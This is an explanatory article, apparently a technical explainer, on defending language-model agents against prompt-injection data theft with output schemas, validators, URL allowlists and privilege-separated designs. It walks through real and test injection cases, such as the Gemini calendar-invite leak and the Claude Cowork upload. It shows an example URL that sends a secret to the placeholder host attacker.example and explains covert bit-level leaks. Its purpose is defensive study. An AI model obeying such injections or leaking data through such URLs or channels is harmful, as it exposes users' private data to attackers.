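# Restricting a language model's output with schemas and URL checks to stop data leaks

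## How a hijacked model leaks data and what an output schema can restrict

Many companies now connect large language models, the programs behind chatbots such as ChatGPT and Claude, to email accounts, calendars, company files and the web. A connected model reads a lot of text written by strangers, some of whom write text that takes control of it. They can then make the model send them any private data it can reach. Developers who use output restriction as a defence assume this takeover will happen and limit what the model can output afterwards. They fix the form of the output in advance, set a rule for each part of it, and have ordinary code check web addresses before anything loads them.

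### Prompt injection

In a prompt injection, an attacker places instructions in content that a model reads, and the model follows them as if they came from its user or developer. The programmer Simon Willison coined the term in 2022 by analogy with SQL injection, an older attack in which a database runs text from a web form as a command. Both attacks work because trusted and untrusted text are mixed, as Willison explains in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025). A model receives the developer's instructions, the user's question and the web page it should summarize as one sequence of tokens (the word fragments that models process), and it cannot reliably distinguish the instructions it should follow from the rest of the text.

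The attacker is usually someone other than the user. In what Microsoft and others call indirect prompt injection, the attacker's instructions reach the model through a web page, an email, a shared document or the result of a tool (a function the model can call, such as web search). The instructions need no special file format, and white text on a white background hides them from the user. Google searched archived copies of the public web and found that malicious injections rose by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026, according to Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild* (2026). Neither Google nor the security firm Forcepoint, which ran its own search, found sophisticated coordinated campaigns.

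Developers have trained models to ignore injected instructions and built filters to catch them. Both help, but neither is guaranteed to stop an attack. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) describes a 2025 attack on ChatGPT that read like a routine office email and worked in half of the tests. Filters usually miss such attacks because detecting one is about as hard as detecting a lie, often without the context needed to expose it.

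Results have improved since then. In an evaluation that Anthropic commissioned in July 2026, none of 720 attempts succeeded against three Claude models in the "auto mode" of Claude Code, the company's programming agent. Writing in August, Willison wanted more independent confirmation. He also described an attack that he did not see how any such mode could stop, in which plausible setup instructions lead the agent to run a malicious software package. Zero successes in 720 independent trials is also compatible with a true success rate of up to about 0.4%, and a determined attacker can try more than 720 times.

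Microsoft calls defences of this kind probabilistic because they make an attack less likely to succeed. A deterministic defence guarantees that a particular attack fails no matter how the model behaves. Restrictions on output are deterministic as long as the code that enforces them is correct and covers every route by which data can leave.

### What a theft requires

An attacker can use an injection to steal data only if three conditions hold together: the model has access to private data, it reads content that the attacker controls, and it can communicate outward. Willison named this combination the "lethal trifecta". Security researchers call the final step exfiltration, moving private data out to someone not entitled to it.

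Removing any one condition prevents the theft, and developers mostly try to remove the third, the route for sending data out. An email assistant that cannot open the mailbox is useless, and one that ignores all outside mail is not much better. Willison argues that outward routes are by far the easiest to restrict without losing that usefulness, and vendors usually fix a reported leak by closing the route. OpenAI built Lockdown Mode, a ChatGPT setting that reached ordinary accounts in June 2026, on the same idea. It limits outgoing network requests but does not stop injections in the text that ChatGPT reads.

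A route for leaking data is easy to miss, though. In January 2026 the security firm Miggo disclosed a flaw in Google's Gemini assistant, which Google has since repaired. The attacker put the injection in a calendar invitation. When the user later asked about the day's meetings, Gemini created a new calendar event and wrote a summary of the user's private meetings in its description. In many company set-ups the attacker could open that event, according to The Hacker News' *Google Gemini Prompt Injection Flaw Exposed Private Calendar Data via Malicious Invites* (2026). A check on web addresses would not have caught the leak.

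### How a web address carries data

The more familiar route is a web address, or URL. Here is a harmless one, adapted from an example in OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026), with an invented phone number as the secret:

`https://attacker.example/collect?data=555-0142`

The host, `attacker.example`, identifies the server that will receive the request. The path, `/collect`, comes next, followed by a question mark and the query. *RFC 3986*, the internet standard for addresses, notes that queries often hold identifying information in "key=value" pairs (Berners-Lee, 2005). A search site might receive the user's search terms that way. A server receives the path and query of every address requested from it, and servers commonly log these requests. The attacker can then read the data in the log, even if there is no page at that address.

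Removing query strings from URLs would not stop the leak, because the phone number could also go in the path or a subdomain.

If the model writes this address as an ordinary link, nothing leaks until the user clicks it, but an image can leak the phone number without a click. Many chat windows display formatted text, in which a model can include an image by giving its address. The user's browser requests that address to load the image, and the request contains the phone number. Link previews in messaging apps can also leak data without a click, because the app fetches the address to show a title or thumbnail. The security firm PromptArmor warns about this risk for agents that people talk to through Slack or Telegram.

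### Secrets going out, instructions coming in

Besides preventing leaks, restricting a model's output can help keep injected instructions from reaching a more privileged model. Some developers divide the work between a quarantined model, which reads untrusted text and cannot act on the world, and a privileged model, which chooses actions and never reads that text directly. The division fails if the quarantined model passes on a free-form summary, since the summary can contain the attacker's instructions.

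Preventing data leaks and preventing prompt injection require separate rules. In *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) label every piece of data in an agent for confidentiality (who may read it) and integrity (whether it comes from a trusted source). Their confidentiality rule lets a message go out only if all its recipients may read its contents. They point out that this rule alone does not prevent prompt injection, because an attacker could still have the agent send a misleading message to colleagues who are entitled to receive it. Blocking that requires an integrity rule that forbids the agent from taking a consequential action if untrusted content influenced the choice.

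Restricting a model's output to integers can block injected commands without preventing leaks. In *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation*, Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues (2025) let a quarantined model return whole numbers, decimals, yes/no values and choices from a fixed list. They argue that none of these types can carry a command to the privileged model, because a command needs some free text. This is persuasive, at least while the numbers are short. They also cap the length of lists, because a long list of numbers could spell out a message for the privileged model to decode, and a very long integer raises the same worry. If the attacker can see the integer and it has no upper limit, the restriction doesn't protect a secret at all, because anyone can encode text as a long number.

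A URL check has the opposite weakness. It can keep the phone number from leaving in a URL but still let a paragraph of injected instructions through to the next model, because the paragraph contains no URL.

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) goes further and argues that any injection that does real harm must either move private data to an unauthorized destination or let untrusted content trigger an action outside the agent's permissions. That seems too strong, because a hijacked model can also give its user a false answer that satisfies every rule about form and destination.

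### Schemas, validators and allowlists

A schema is a machine-readable description of the fields an output may contain and the values each may take. Developers often write schemas for JSON, a text format that stores data as labelled fields. *JSON Schema* (2026), a working draft from the internet standards body IETF, defines a schema as a JSON document that describes and constrains other JSON documents. A field rule restricts the value of one field. In JSON Schema (2020), the keyword `type` can require a whole number or a true/false value, and `enum` lists the permitted values. Other rules set a number range or a maximum length.

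For example, a model that sorts incoming email might have a schema with a `category` field that allows four words, an `urgent` field that is true or false, and a `reply_days` field that takes a whole number from 0 to 30. An attacker who hijacks this model can make it mislabel every message in the inbox, but can't make it output a web address, because no field accepts one.

A schema is enforced by a validator, which is ordinary program code that accepts or rejects a model's output before anything else uses it. The validator checks the output against the schema's rules and doesn't try to detect injections. Checking rules is far easier, because code can test whether a number is between 0 and 30, but attackers can word an instruction in endless ways. O'Reilly's *Beyond Prompt Injection* says the check must be deterministic code rather than a second model that looks for danger, because an injection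 could work on the second model too.

The usual rule for destinations is an allowlist, which permits listed destinations and refuses all others. Even a list of trusted sites can let data reach an attacker. OpenAI notes that many reputable sites offer redirects, which forward a visitor to another address, so a request can start at a permitted site and end at the attacker's. A permitted site may also let anyone, including the attacker, open an account. Willison reported in January 2026 that PromptArmor got files out of Claude Cowork, an Anthropic agent, by having it upload them to Anthropic's own servers under the attacker's account.

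Web browsers have their own allowlist mechanism, the content security policy (CSP), in which a web page names the domains from which images and other content may load. If the policy for a chat page omits `attacker.example`, the browser will not request a picture from there, whatever the model writes. Microsoft used a CSP in May 2023 to stop its Bing Chat from leaking data through images, according to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*. A CSP governs what the page loads, so it does not help when an agent fetches an address from a company's server. W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), the current draft of the standard, recommends CSP as an extra layer of defence against injected content, not as the first line.

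### Measuring what gets through

Some outputs leave an attacker far more room than others, and a single number expresses the difference. The capacity of an output is the most information it can carry, in bits. If the rules allow N different outputs, then

capacity = log₂ N.

A yes/no field allows two outputs, and log₂ 2 = 1, so it carries 1 bit. For a text field of 200 characters, suppose that each character can be any of the 95 printable characters in ASCII, the basic English character set. That allows 95²⁰⁰ different texts, and

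200 × log₂ 95 ≈ 200 × 6.57 ≈ 1,314 bits.

Also allowing shorter texts adds less than a tenth of a bit to the field's capacity. A sixteen-digit card number takes about 53 bits, so one such field can hold 24 of them if the attacker packs them efficiently. An integer with about 396 digits can carry as much information as the text field, so the integers above need an upper limit.

When an output has several independent fields, their capacities in bits add up, because the numbers of possible values multiply. The email sorter's three fields allow 4 × 2 × 31 = 248 outputs, or just under 8 bits. Adding a 200-character `note` field raises the total to about 1,322 bits, nearly all of it from the note.

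*Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (Metere, 2026) applies the same measure to agents' tool calls. The logarithm is an upper bound because randomness in the model's output can only reduce what the receiver learns. The bound holds however the attacker words the injection, since processing a message cannot add information to it. Metere also counts a refusal as a possible output. If an attacker can tell when the validator rejects something, a yes/no field has three outcomes and carries up to log₂ 3 ≈ 1.58 bits.

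A count of field values can miss leaks through tool calls as well as through refusals. Microsoft observes that when an attacker can see whether a model called a tool, the call leaks one bit regardless of what it contains. The system built by Costa and colleagues leaves the order and timing of tool calls unprotected because a stricter rule would forbid too much useful work.

Small leaks also add up. An attacker who can run the model twenty times on the same secret, getting one yes/no answer each time, can learn any six-digit security code, because twenty such answers distinguish 2²⁰ = 1,048,576 possibilities. To limit the total, the monitor in *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress* (2026) gives each destination an allowance of bits that refills at a set rate, and it delays or cancels suspicious messages once the allowance runs out. Such limits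 don't help much if the secret is itself a yes or a no, such as whether a company intends to buy a rival.

The risk of a leak depends on where the output goes as well as on its capacity. A 1,314-bit text field that appears only on the user's own screen, as plain text, gives an attacker nothing directly, but even a single bit in an attacker's server log is a leak. For each system and product flaw below, we therefore consider what information a model under an attacker's full control can still emit and who receives it.

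## What schema enforcement guarantees: tests on ordering agents and nine models

The capacity figures above hold only if every output follows its schema. Developers can get structured output from a model by asking for it in the prompt, validating the output afterwards, or using constrained decoding.

A developer can request structured output by pasting the schema into the prompt and telling the model to reply in that form, but a hijacked model can fail to follow the instruction. With validation, a validator checks the model's finished output against the schema, often giving the model another try if the check fails. Constrained decoding blocks, at each step of generation, every token that would make the output break the schema. Validation and constrained decoding are both deterministic, and many developers use them together.

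OpenAI's older JSON mode guarantees valid JSON but not a match to any particular schema, according to *Introducing Structured Outputs in the API* (OpenAI, 2024). A hijacked model in JSON mode could add an extra field and put a stolen phone number in it. Providers offer full schema enforcement mainly so that programs can read a model's output without errors, and protection against leaks is a side effect.

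### Constrained decoding step by step

Here is a schema for a cut-down email sorter that has only a `category` field:

```json
{
  "type": "object",
  "properties": {
    "category": {"enum": ["billing", "sales", "spam", "support"]}
  },
  "required": ["category"],
  "additionalProperties": false
}
```

Before generation starts, software compiles the schema into a grammar, a set of rules for what may come next at each point in the output. For simple patterns, the grammar can be a finite-state machine, which is a list of positions with the permitted moves from each. *Why Does Structured Output Fail?* (Verma, 2026) explains that nested structures need a pushdown automaton, which also tracks which brackets are still open. Compiling takes time, so the first request with a new schema is slower. Anthropic's *Structured outputs* says the company keeps each compiled grammar for 24 hours after its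 last use.

Real models have vocabularies of many thousands of tokens. Suppose that this one has only ten: `{"category":"`, `bill`, `ing`, `sales`, `sp`, `am`, `support`, `https`, `"}` and a marker that ends the output. If the model picks `spam`, generation goes like this:

| Output so far | Tokens allowed next | Tokens blocked |
|---|---|---|
| Nothing | `{"category":"` | The other nine |
| `{"category":"` | `bill`, `sales`, `sp`, `support` | `ing`, `am`, `https`, `"}`, the opening text, the end marker |
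| `{"category":"sp` | `am` | The other nine |
| `{"category":"spam` | `"}` | The other nine |
| `{"category":"spam"}` | The end marker | The other nine |

Now suppose an injection has told the model to write a web address in this field. At the second step, the model gives `https` a probability of 0.90, `sp` 0.06, `sales` 0.02, and `bill` and `support` 0.01 each. The software sets the probability of every blocked token to zero and rescales the rest. For an allowed token t,

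new p(t) = p(t) / (sum of p over all allowed tokens).

The allowed tokens' probabilities add up to 0.10, so `sp` rises to 0.6, `sales` to 0.2, and `bill` and `support` to 0.1 each. The model can no longer output the web address. The attacker may still be able to control which of the four words it outputs, so the field can carry log₂ 4 = 2 bits.

The grammar Anthropic applies to a model's reply does not cover its tool calls, so a hijacked agent whose reply follows a strict schema could still put the phone number in a web search. Developers can turn on enforcement for tool inputs separately, for at most 20 tools per request.

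Replies can also break the schema when the model refuses a request or runs out of tokens. A refusal is free text, and Anthropic's API returns it with the same status code as a successful reply, so a program that doesn't check why generation stopped could forward unrestricted text.

### Which rules need a validator

Providers enforce different field rules during generation. The table below compares Anthropic's rules with those in OpenAI's *Structured outputs*, Google Cloud's *Structured output* and AWS's documentation for Bedrock, its model-hosting service.

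| Field rule | Anthropic | OpenAI | Google Cloud | AWS |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Fixed list | Yes, except capitalization | Yes | Yes, text values only | Yes |
| Text pattern | Simple patterns | Yes | No | Most patterns |
| Number range | No | Yes | Yes | No |
| Text length | No | Unclear | No | No |
| Maximum list size | No | Yes | Yes | No |

OpenAI is unclear about whether a schema can limit the length of text. Its list of supported text rules omits length limits, but it says fine-tuned models "additionally" lack them, which suggests that other models support them. Dottxt, a rival provider, lists them as supported in its comparison. A developer who relies on a length limit to contain leaks should test it or check the length in a validator.

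The lack of support for number ranges affects the full email sorter, whose `reply_days` field takes a whole number from 0 to 30. Anthropic's service rejects a schema that contains such a range. Most of the company's helper libraries therefore move the range into the field's description, which the model can ignore. Some helpers then check the reply against the original range, but one TypeScript helper for plain JSON schemas does not. Without that check, the number has no upper limit and can carry as much data as a long text field. Listing all 31 allowed values in the schema avoids the problem, because Anthropic enforces fixed lists.

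Google Cloud ignores schema rules it does not support and still processes the request. If a developer sets a maximum length of 200 characters, Google Cloud does not enforce the limit or return an error. The sample code in Google's *Structured outputs*, a guide for Gemini developers, runs each reply through a validator even though the schema has already constrained the output.

Other rules restrict output less than a developer might expect. Anthropic and AWS both support a `uri` format, but it only requires a well-formed address, so the attacker's address with the phone number in it passes. Anthropic warns that a value from a fixed list may come back with different capitalization. A validator can ignore case when comparing values and then pass on the developer's own spelling, so that the capitals can't carry information. Rules that compare one field with another also need a validator, because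 JSON Schema generally cannot express them.

### Nine models asked to follow a schema

In August 2026, Verma measured how often nine OpenAI and Anthropic models break a schema when nobody is attacking them and constrained decoding is off. The questions came from two public collections, HotpotQA (general knowledge) and FinanceBench (company finances). For each question, a model first identified the people, places or organizations involved, then gathered facts about them, and finally wrote an answer. The prompt for each step included that step's own schema and an instruction to return only JSON. Pydantic, a Python validation library, checked every output. After a failure, the model was given the error and up to three more attempts.

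Of 3,997 attempts, 1,126 failed, or 28.2%. Claude Haiku 4.5 alone produced 878 of the failures, and without it the rate was 9.3%. These are the rates under the main schema:

| Model | Failed attempts | Most common failure |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 66.1% | Code fence around the JSON |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 21.4% | Code fence around the JSON |
| GPT-4o | 16.0% | Returned the schema itself |
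| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 15.7% | Text too long |
| GPT-4o mini | 13.6% | Text pattern broken |
| GPT-5.6 Terra | 5.3% | Text pattern broken |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 4.9% | Text too long |
| GPT-5.6 Luna | 4.1% | Text pattern broken |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 3.5% | Text pattern broken |

In 681 of the failures, the model added a code fence, the row of backticks that marks a block of code in formatted text, although the prompt told it not to. Another 263 failures were mainly about length and 126 about patterns. For example, one GPT-5.6 model turned a street address into the identifier `888_7th_avenue`, which broke a rule that identifiers start with a letter. In 38 cases the model returned the schema instead of filling it in, and in nine it put prose before the JSON. Only eight failures were mainly about a value outside a fixed list. The remaining failure was an empty reply.

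Many of the fenced outputs also contained text that was too long. When Verma removed the fences and checked again, only 48% passed, and nearly all the others had this second fault. The first error message had not mentioned length, only that the JSON was unreadable. Retries still fixed most failures, and 948 of 973 runs completed all three steps. All 24 of Haiku 4.5's incomplete runs ended on a length error.

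Length limits therefore cause many of the failures by honest models, and they are also the rule that providers enforce least. When Verma rechecked Sonnet 4.6's outputs against higher limits, the failure rate fell from 15.7% to 5.6%. But one of those limits rose from 250 to 1,000 characters, which increases the field's capacity from about 1,640 bits to 6,570. Where the text could reach an attacker, a shorter limit is better despite the extra rejections, and a fixed list of allowed values is better still.

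### Valid orders with the wrong contents

Verma did not check whether the outputs that passed were correct. Li (2026) checked this for restaurant orders in *When JSON Is Not Enough*. The benchmark has a seven-item menu and 300 customer requests, split evenly among ten categories such as simple orders, allergy conflicts and dishes not on the menu. For each request, the model fills in a JSON object with the items, the customer's dietary constraints and a status, which can be accepted, needs clarification or rejected for safety. Li wrote the correct answers by hand and used ordinary code to compare the model's outputs with them.

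Four open-weight models handled every request twice, once with the schema only in the prompt and once with the provider enforcing it as well. An order counted as correct only if its status, items, quantities, changes and constraints all matched exactly. An unsafe acceptance was an accepted order that the restaurant should not have carried out, because it conflicted with an allergy or diet or asked for something unavailable. Each cell gives the result for prompting alone, then for enforcement:

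| Model | Followed the schema | Correct order | Unsafe acceptance |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-OSS 120B | 100%, 100% | 83.0%, 81.3% | 0.3%, 0.0% |
| Qwen3-30B | 100%, 100% | 31.3%, 30.7% | 15.0%, 14.3% |
| Llama-3.1-8B | 68.7%, 100% | 31.7%, 36.0% | 13.3%, 8.3% |
| Gemma-2-2B | 91.7%, 100% | 0.0%, 2.0% | 45.0%, 41.7% |

Enforcement made every output follow the schema but left correctness almost unchanged. For GPT-OSS 120B, the strongest model, the number of correct orders differed by five out of 300, which chance could easily explain (p = 0.458). This model already followed the schema every time without enforcement. It got most requests with a dietary conflict wrong either way, scoring 40% with prompting alone and 37% with enforcement.

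Enforcement reduced unsafe acceptances for the two smallest models. Llama-3.1-8B's fell from 40 to 25, a drop unlikely to be due to chance (p = 0.001). But the share of its orders with the right status also fell, from 74.3% to 69.7%, so it must have held back more good orders or more often confused asking for clarification with rejecting.

The menu is small, the requests are artificial and all four models are well behind today's best, so these error rates are a poor guide to current products. But the reason for the errors applies to any model, because a schema constrains only the output. In one test, a customer with a peanut allergy ordered satay noodles, and Gemma accepted the order under enforcement. The same JSON items would be correct for a customer without the allergy, so the schema can't catch the error. Catching it takes code that also checks the ingredients against the customer's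 allergies, and Li recommends such a check before any order goes through.

OpenAI warns that a model may invent values when the input is unrelated to the schema, because it always tries to fill in the fields. Adding a value such as `unclear` to a fixed list gives the model an accurate option for such inputs and adds very little capacity to leak data.

### Schema violations as a warning sign

A reply that violates its schema can be evidence of an attack. *Clouding the Mirror* (Koide, Nakano and Chiba, 2026) studies models that judge whether a website is a phishing site, a fake page built to steal passwords. The attacker controls the page the model reads, and can use injections to persuade the model that the page is harmless, or to make it refuse or answer in a format that the next program cannot read. The paper's defence, InjectDefuser, checks each reply against a schema, repairs minor formatting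 errors and treats major violations as possible signs of manipulation.

The full defence also includes a hardened prompt and a list of brands' genuine domains. On 2,000 test pages, it cut the attack success rate from 39.9% to 0.3% for GPT-5, but only from 84.7% to 61.7% for Llama 4 Maverick. These figures cover all three parts together, so it is unclear how much of the drop came from validation. Validation can't have done much against the most effective attacks, which presented the page as something legitimate, such as security training, because a model misled by them still returns a valid reply with the wrong answer.

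A schema violation is also weaker evidence of an injection if the model often breaks the schema by itself. Suppose one page in 1,000 contains an injection, and that injection always breaks the schema. A model with GPT-5.6 Sol's failure rate of 3.5% would also produce about 35 violations per 1,000 pages by itself, so fewer than 3% of violations would come from injections. Values outside a fixed list are a better signal. Verma recorded them as the main fault in only 0.2% of attempts, and at that rate about one such violation in three would come from an injection.

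Constrained decoding removes this signal. In the example above, the hijacked sorter gave a web address a 90% probability, yet the program received an ordinary category such as `spam`. A developer who runs the model directly could log the total probability on blocked tokens and investigate high values. Models that haven't been hijacked would also produce high values at times, for instance when they give a high probability to a code fence.

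Even with constrained decoding, a refusal or a reply that hits the token limit can be a sign of an injection. Koide and colleagues tested attacks that aimed for each, but both can also happen without an attack. An OpenAI employee quoted by Willison said in 2024 that a confused model under enforcement can get stuck in a loop of technically valid output.

A developer who wants both the limit and the warning can leave the model unconstrained and have a validator reject every violation. Visible rejections barely increase the capacity, adding less than 0.01 bits for the three-field email sorter. The drawback is that the validator also rejects honest outputs that break the schema, which is tolerable at GPT-5.6 Sol's failure rate but not at Haiku 4.5's.

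### Repairing and rejecting

A validator that finds a violation can reject the output or repair it. Removing a code fence is fairly safe if the validator then checks the full contents, because doing so doesn't change the values. More than half of the fenced outputs in Verma's test would have failed that check.

Repairs that change a value are riskier. If code shortens an overlong text to 200 characters, the attacker still gets 200 characters through. If code searches a longer reply for the first thing that looks like JSON, the attacker can choose what it finds. Some validators make repairs by default. Pydantic, for example, converts some values to the expected type and drops unknown fields.

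A repair can also turn an obvious error into a hidden one. One of Li's customers asked for a burger with pineapple, which the restaurant does not offer. Deleting the pineapple would produce a valid order that the customer never placed. For fields that affect safety, Li advises stopping the order and asking the customer.

With retries, the repair code doesn't have to guess what the model meant, and they work well for ordinary mistakes. In Verma's test, Haiku 4.5 failed on its first attempt in all 475 cases, but retrying produced a valid output in 451. After an injection, however, the attacker's text is still in the model's context, and the hijacked model can read in the error message which rule blocked its output. A system that reads untrusted text should therefore allow few retries and record each one.

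A system also needs a safe fallback for when it rejects a reply. Koide and colleagues count a malformed reply as a success for the attacker, because the phishing page goes unflagged. A detector that rejects such a reply should block the page or send it to a person for review.

### Why the schema must come from trusted code

A schema restricts a model's output, and the model also reads it. Each field can have a description in ordinary language, and Google Cloud says its models use field names and descriptions when generating a reply. Lin (2026), in *Your Prompt Is Not the Only Prompt*, measured how strongly descriptions affect the result.

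The task was to sort 48 short workplace messages into four categories by the structure of their arguments, such as conclusion first and reason second. The categories had made-up names such as "tomil" and "varek", so a model could not guess their meaning. Lin put the correct definitions in the system prompt, which holds the developer's standing instructions to the model. In the conflict test, the schema descriptions paired the same definitions with the wrong categories.

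The wrong descriptions cut Claude Haiku 4.5's accuracy from 52.5% to 7.1%. Random guessing would score 25%, so the model was mostly following the schema rather than the developer's instructions. GPT-5.5 fell from 100% to 73.3%, and Claude Sonnet 4.6 from 83.8% to 65.8%. GPT-4.1 lost only three points, and GPT-5.4 improved slightly. The figures are rough because the test used 48 messages, but the largest drops are far too big to be noise.

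Lin's tests involved no attacker, but they imply that anyone who can write a schema description can give some models instructions. An outsider could do this if a program builds its schema from the column headings of a downloaded spreadsheet or takes a tool's schema from an outside supplier. The outsider could also loosen the rules, for example by replacing a fixed list with free text, and constrained decoding would then enforce the looser version. A fixed list is also unsafe if the program fills it with subject lines from the inbox, because an attacker could have written one of them. Descriptions, rules and permitted values should all come from the developer's own code, and the validator should keep its own copy of them.

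Lin also found that adding a required text field, in which the model explains its reasoning before it picks a category, raised GPT-4.1's accuracy from 77.1% to 97.9% and Haiku 4.5's from 53.8% to 77.5%. But the field makes the schema less strict, and it can carry stolen data or injected instructions. The developer can keep most of the benefit by having the validator delete the explanation before any other model, log or user interface receives the output.

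## Three agents that read untrusted text through restricted fields

The email sorter only labels messages, but an agent that shops, arranges meetings or fixes bugs has to act on what it reads, so restricting its final reply is not enough. Its developer can have a quarantined model read the untrusted text and a privileged model choose the actions, with a schema limiting what passes between them. Jacob and colleagues built three agents this way and attacked each one. No attack succeeded, but the bug-fixing agent fixed about a third fewer bugs than without the defence.

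### Variables that the privileged model cannot read

Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, proposed dividing an assistant between two models. Ordinary software, which he calls the controller, runs both models and stores their results in named variables. If the user asks for a summary of the latest email, the design works like this:

1. The privileged model asks the controller to fetch the email and store it as `$VAR1`.
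2. The privileged model asks for a summary of `$VAR1`. The controller inserts the email into a prompt for the quarantined model and stores the reply as `$VAR2`.
3. The privileged model tells the controller to display `$VAR2`, and the controller shows the user the text.

The privileged model receives only the names of the variables, so an instruction hidden in the email can distort the summary but can't reach the model that controls the tools. Willison made one exception, allowing the privileged model to read an answer chosen from a fixed set of categories after code has checked it.

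He also called his own solution "pretty bad". It is complicated to build, and a single mistake that lets untrusted text through defeats it. A hijacked summary can also persuade the user to paste private data into the attacker's website.

A variable can also carry a wrong value into an action. For example, a user might ask the agent to send Bob a document and say that Bob's email address is in the meeting notes. An injection in the notes can make the quarantined model return the attacker's address instead of Bob's. The privileged model then sends the document to that address without seeing it.

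Debenedetti and colleagues described this flaw in 2025 and built CaMeL, a Google DeepMind system, to fix it. Willison explains how it works in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (2025). The privileged model writes its plan as a program in a restricted version of Python, and a custom interpreter tracks where each value came from and who may read it. A policy can then allow emails to trusted recipients and require the user's approval for any others. But someone has to write and maintain the policies, and people who see many approval requests tend to approve them all.

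FIDES, the Microsoft system from Costa and colleagues, hides a tool's result in a variable only if showing it would make the privileged model's context less trusted or more confidential. The privileged model can ask a quarantined model about the hidden text and set a schema for the answer. FIDES ranks answer types by how much information they can carry, from yes/no to a choice from a fixed list to free text. A policy may let a yes/no answer from untrusted text influence an action because the answer carries only one bit. That bit can still do harm if it determines whether the agent pays an invoice.

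On AgentDojo, a public set of tests for tool-using agents under attack, FIDES stopped every injection when its policies were on. It completed 8% more tasks on average than a basic agent with GPT-4o, and 16% more with OpenAI's o1. FIDES combines restricted answers with labels and policies, while Jacob and colleagues rely on the restricted fields themselves to keep instructions out.

### Four permitted types

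Jacob and colleagues call their method type-directed privilege separation. The quarantined model may pass the privileged model only whole numbers, decimals, yes/no values and choices from a fixed list, or a list or object that combines them. This set of fields is called a handoff, and constrained decoding enforces its schema. The quarantined model can also fill variables that the privileged model cannot read, as in Willison's design. The privileged model can send the quarantined model any information, because a hijacked quarantined model has no way to act.

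The protection comes from the permitted types, not the JSON format. *Agent Privilege Separation in OpenClaw* (2026) describes a system in which one agent reads untrusted content and sends JSON summaries to a second agent, which has the tools. Injected content appeared in 63.7% of the summaries. None of the attacks succeeded, but the paper warns that the defence would weaken if attackers found instructions that the second agent follows even inside JSON fields. Attackers could not put such instructions in a handoff that has no free text.

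Jacob and colleagues compared each of their three agents with an ordinary version that reads the untrusted text directly. They measured the tasks completed when nobody was attacking, then the attack success rate:

| Agent | Model | Tasks completed, undefended | Tasks completed, defended | Attack success, undefended | Attack success, defended |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Shopping | GPT-4o | 21.8% | 22.4% | 31.7% | 0% |
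| Calendar | GPT-4o | 90.0% | 91.0% | 63.0% | 0% |
| Bug fixing | GPT-5.2 | 68.3% | 45.0% | 98.9% | 0% |

### The shopping agent

The shopping agent works in WebShop, a simulated online shop with about 1.2 million real products. It receives a request for a product with certain features and a certain price, searches the shop and buys the item that fits best. Strangers write the product reviews, so those are the untrusted text. In the defended version, the quarantined model reads each review separately and returns two whole numbers:

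- `review_support`, from 0 to 10, measures how strongly the review recommends the product.
- `review_relevance`, from 0 to 10, measures whether the review is coherent and about this product.

The privileged agent takes the median of each score. It uses the two medians, the number of reviews and the rest of the product page to choose its next click.

Jacob and colleagues tested 500 requests. For each one, they added an injection to a single review of the product the agent should buy, telling the agent to leave the page and choose something else. They ran every request five times and counted an outcome if it occurred in at least three runs. The attack success rate covers only requests for which the agent had found the right product before the attack.

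The defence did not reduce the number of successful purchases, and the difference in the table is three requests. But this is weak evidence that two scores can replace the text of a review. WebShop has no reviews of its own, so Jacob and colleagues had GPT-4o write them. Since the shop grades a purchase on the product's features and price, an agent could probably have ignored the reviews and done just as well.

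The privileged agent also reads the seller's product description in full. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) points out that a hotel's description could contain an injection aimed at a booking agent. A dishonest seller could attack the shopping agent the same way, and restricting the reviews would not prevent this.

### The calendar agent

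The calendar agent arranges a meeting by exchanging emails with another person, who may be the attacker. The undefended agent reads this person's emails alongside the user's calendar, so an injection can make it send out private details. In the defended version, the quarantined model reads the email thread and fills in two fields:

- `suggested_time_list` is a list of the times that the other person has proposed, each chosen from a fixed list of slots.
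- `meeting_description` is free text about the meeting, such as its subject and location. It goes into a variable that the privileged model cannot read.

The privileged model sees the proposed times and the user's calendar and can either reply or finish. If it replies, it chooses times that might suit both people, and a separate model writes the email. If it finishes, it adds the meeting to the calendar, and the description is filled in from the variable.

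Jacob and colleagues generated 200 weekly calendars, each with 10 to 30 events in one-hour slots, and paired them at random to make 100 email threads. They put a marker phrase in every event description and counted an attack as successful if the phrase appeared in any email from the user's agent. The undefended agent leaked the phrase in 63 threads, and the defended agent leaked it in none.

Without an attack, the defended agent found a time that suited both calendars in 91 threads, and the undefended agent did so in 90. The handoff doesn't lower the success rate here because the agent needs little from the emails except the times.

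### The bug-fixing agent

The bug-fixing agent reads a bug report from GitHub, a site where developers share code, and writes a repair. On a public project, anyone can file a report. The undefended agent reads the report and can run any command on a copy of the code. In the defended version, the quarantined model reads the report, explores the code and fills in these fields:

- `bug_category` is one of 52 types of bug, such as an off-by-one error or a memory leak.
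- `fix_scope` is one of three values: a small local fix, a fix in several places or a complex fix.
- `code_regions` is a list of suspicious places in the code.

Each item in `code_regions` has four fields of its own:

- `file_index` is the file's number in a sorted list of all the project's files. Ordinary code later replaces it with the file's path.
- `role` is one of eight values, such as the suspected source of the bug or a test that covers it.
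- `start_line` and `end_line` are whole numbers.

A planner model uses the handoff and a clean copy of the code to write three repair plans. The plans can be in ordinary language because the planner never sees the bug report, which contains the attacker's text. A judge model reads the report and compares the plans but can return only the number of the best one. The privileged agent then receives the handoff and the chosen plan and repairs another clean copy of the code.

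Jacob and colleagues tested the agent on SWE-bench Lite, a collection of 300 real GitHub issues. They removed feature requests, set 52 issues aside for developing the agent and dropped three that caused errors, which left 180. They ended each issue with an injection telling the agent to create an unrelated file. The undefended agent created the file in 178 cases and the defended agent in none.

The defended agent fixed 81 bugs, while the undefended one fixed 123. Jacob and colleagues attribute the gap to the loss of the report's text, which matters a lot in real bug repair. A handoff can identify an off-by-one error in lines 40 to 60 of a file, but it has no field for the input that triggers the error, the error message or the result the user expected, so the privileged agent has to work these out from the code.

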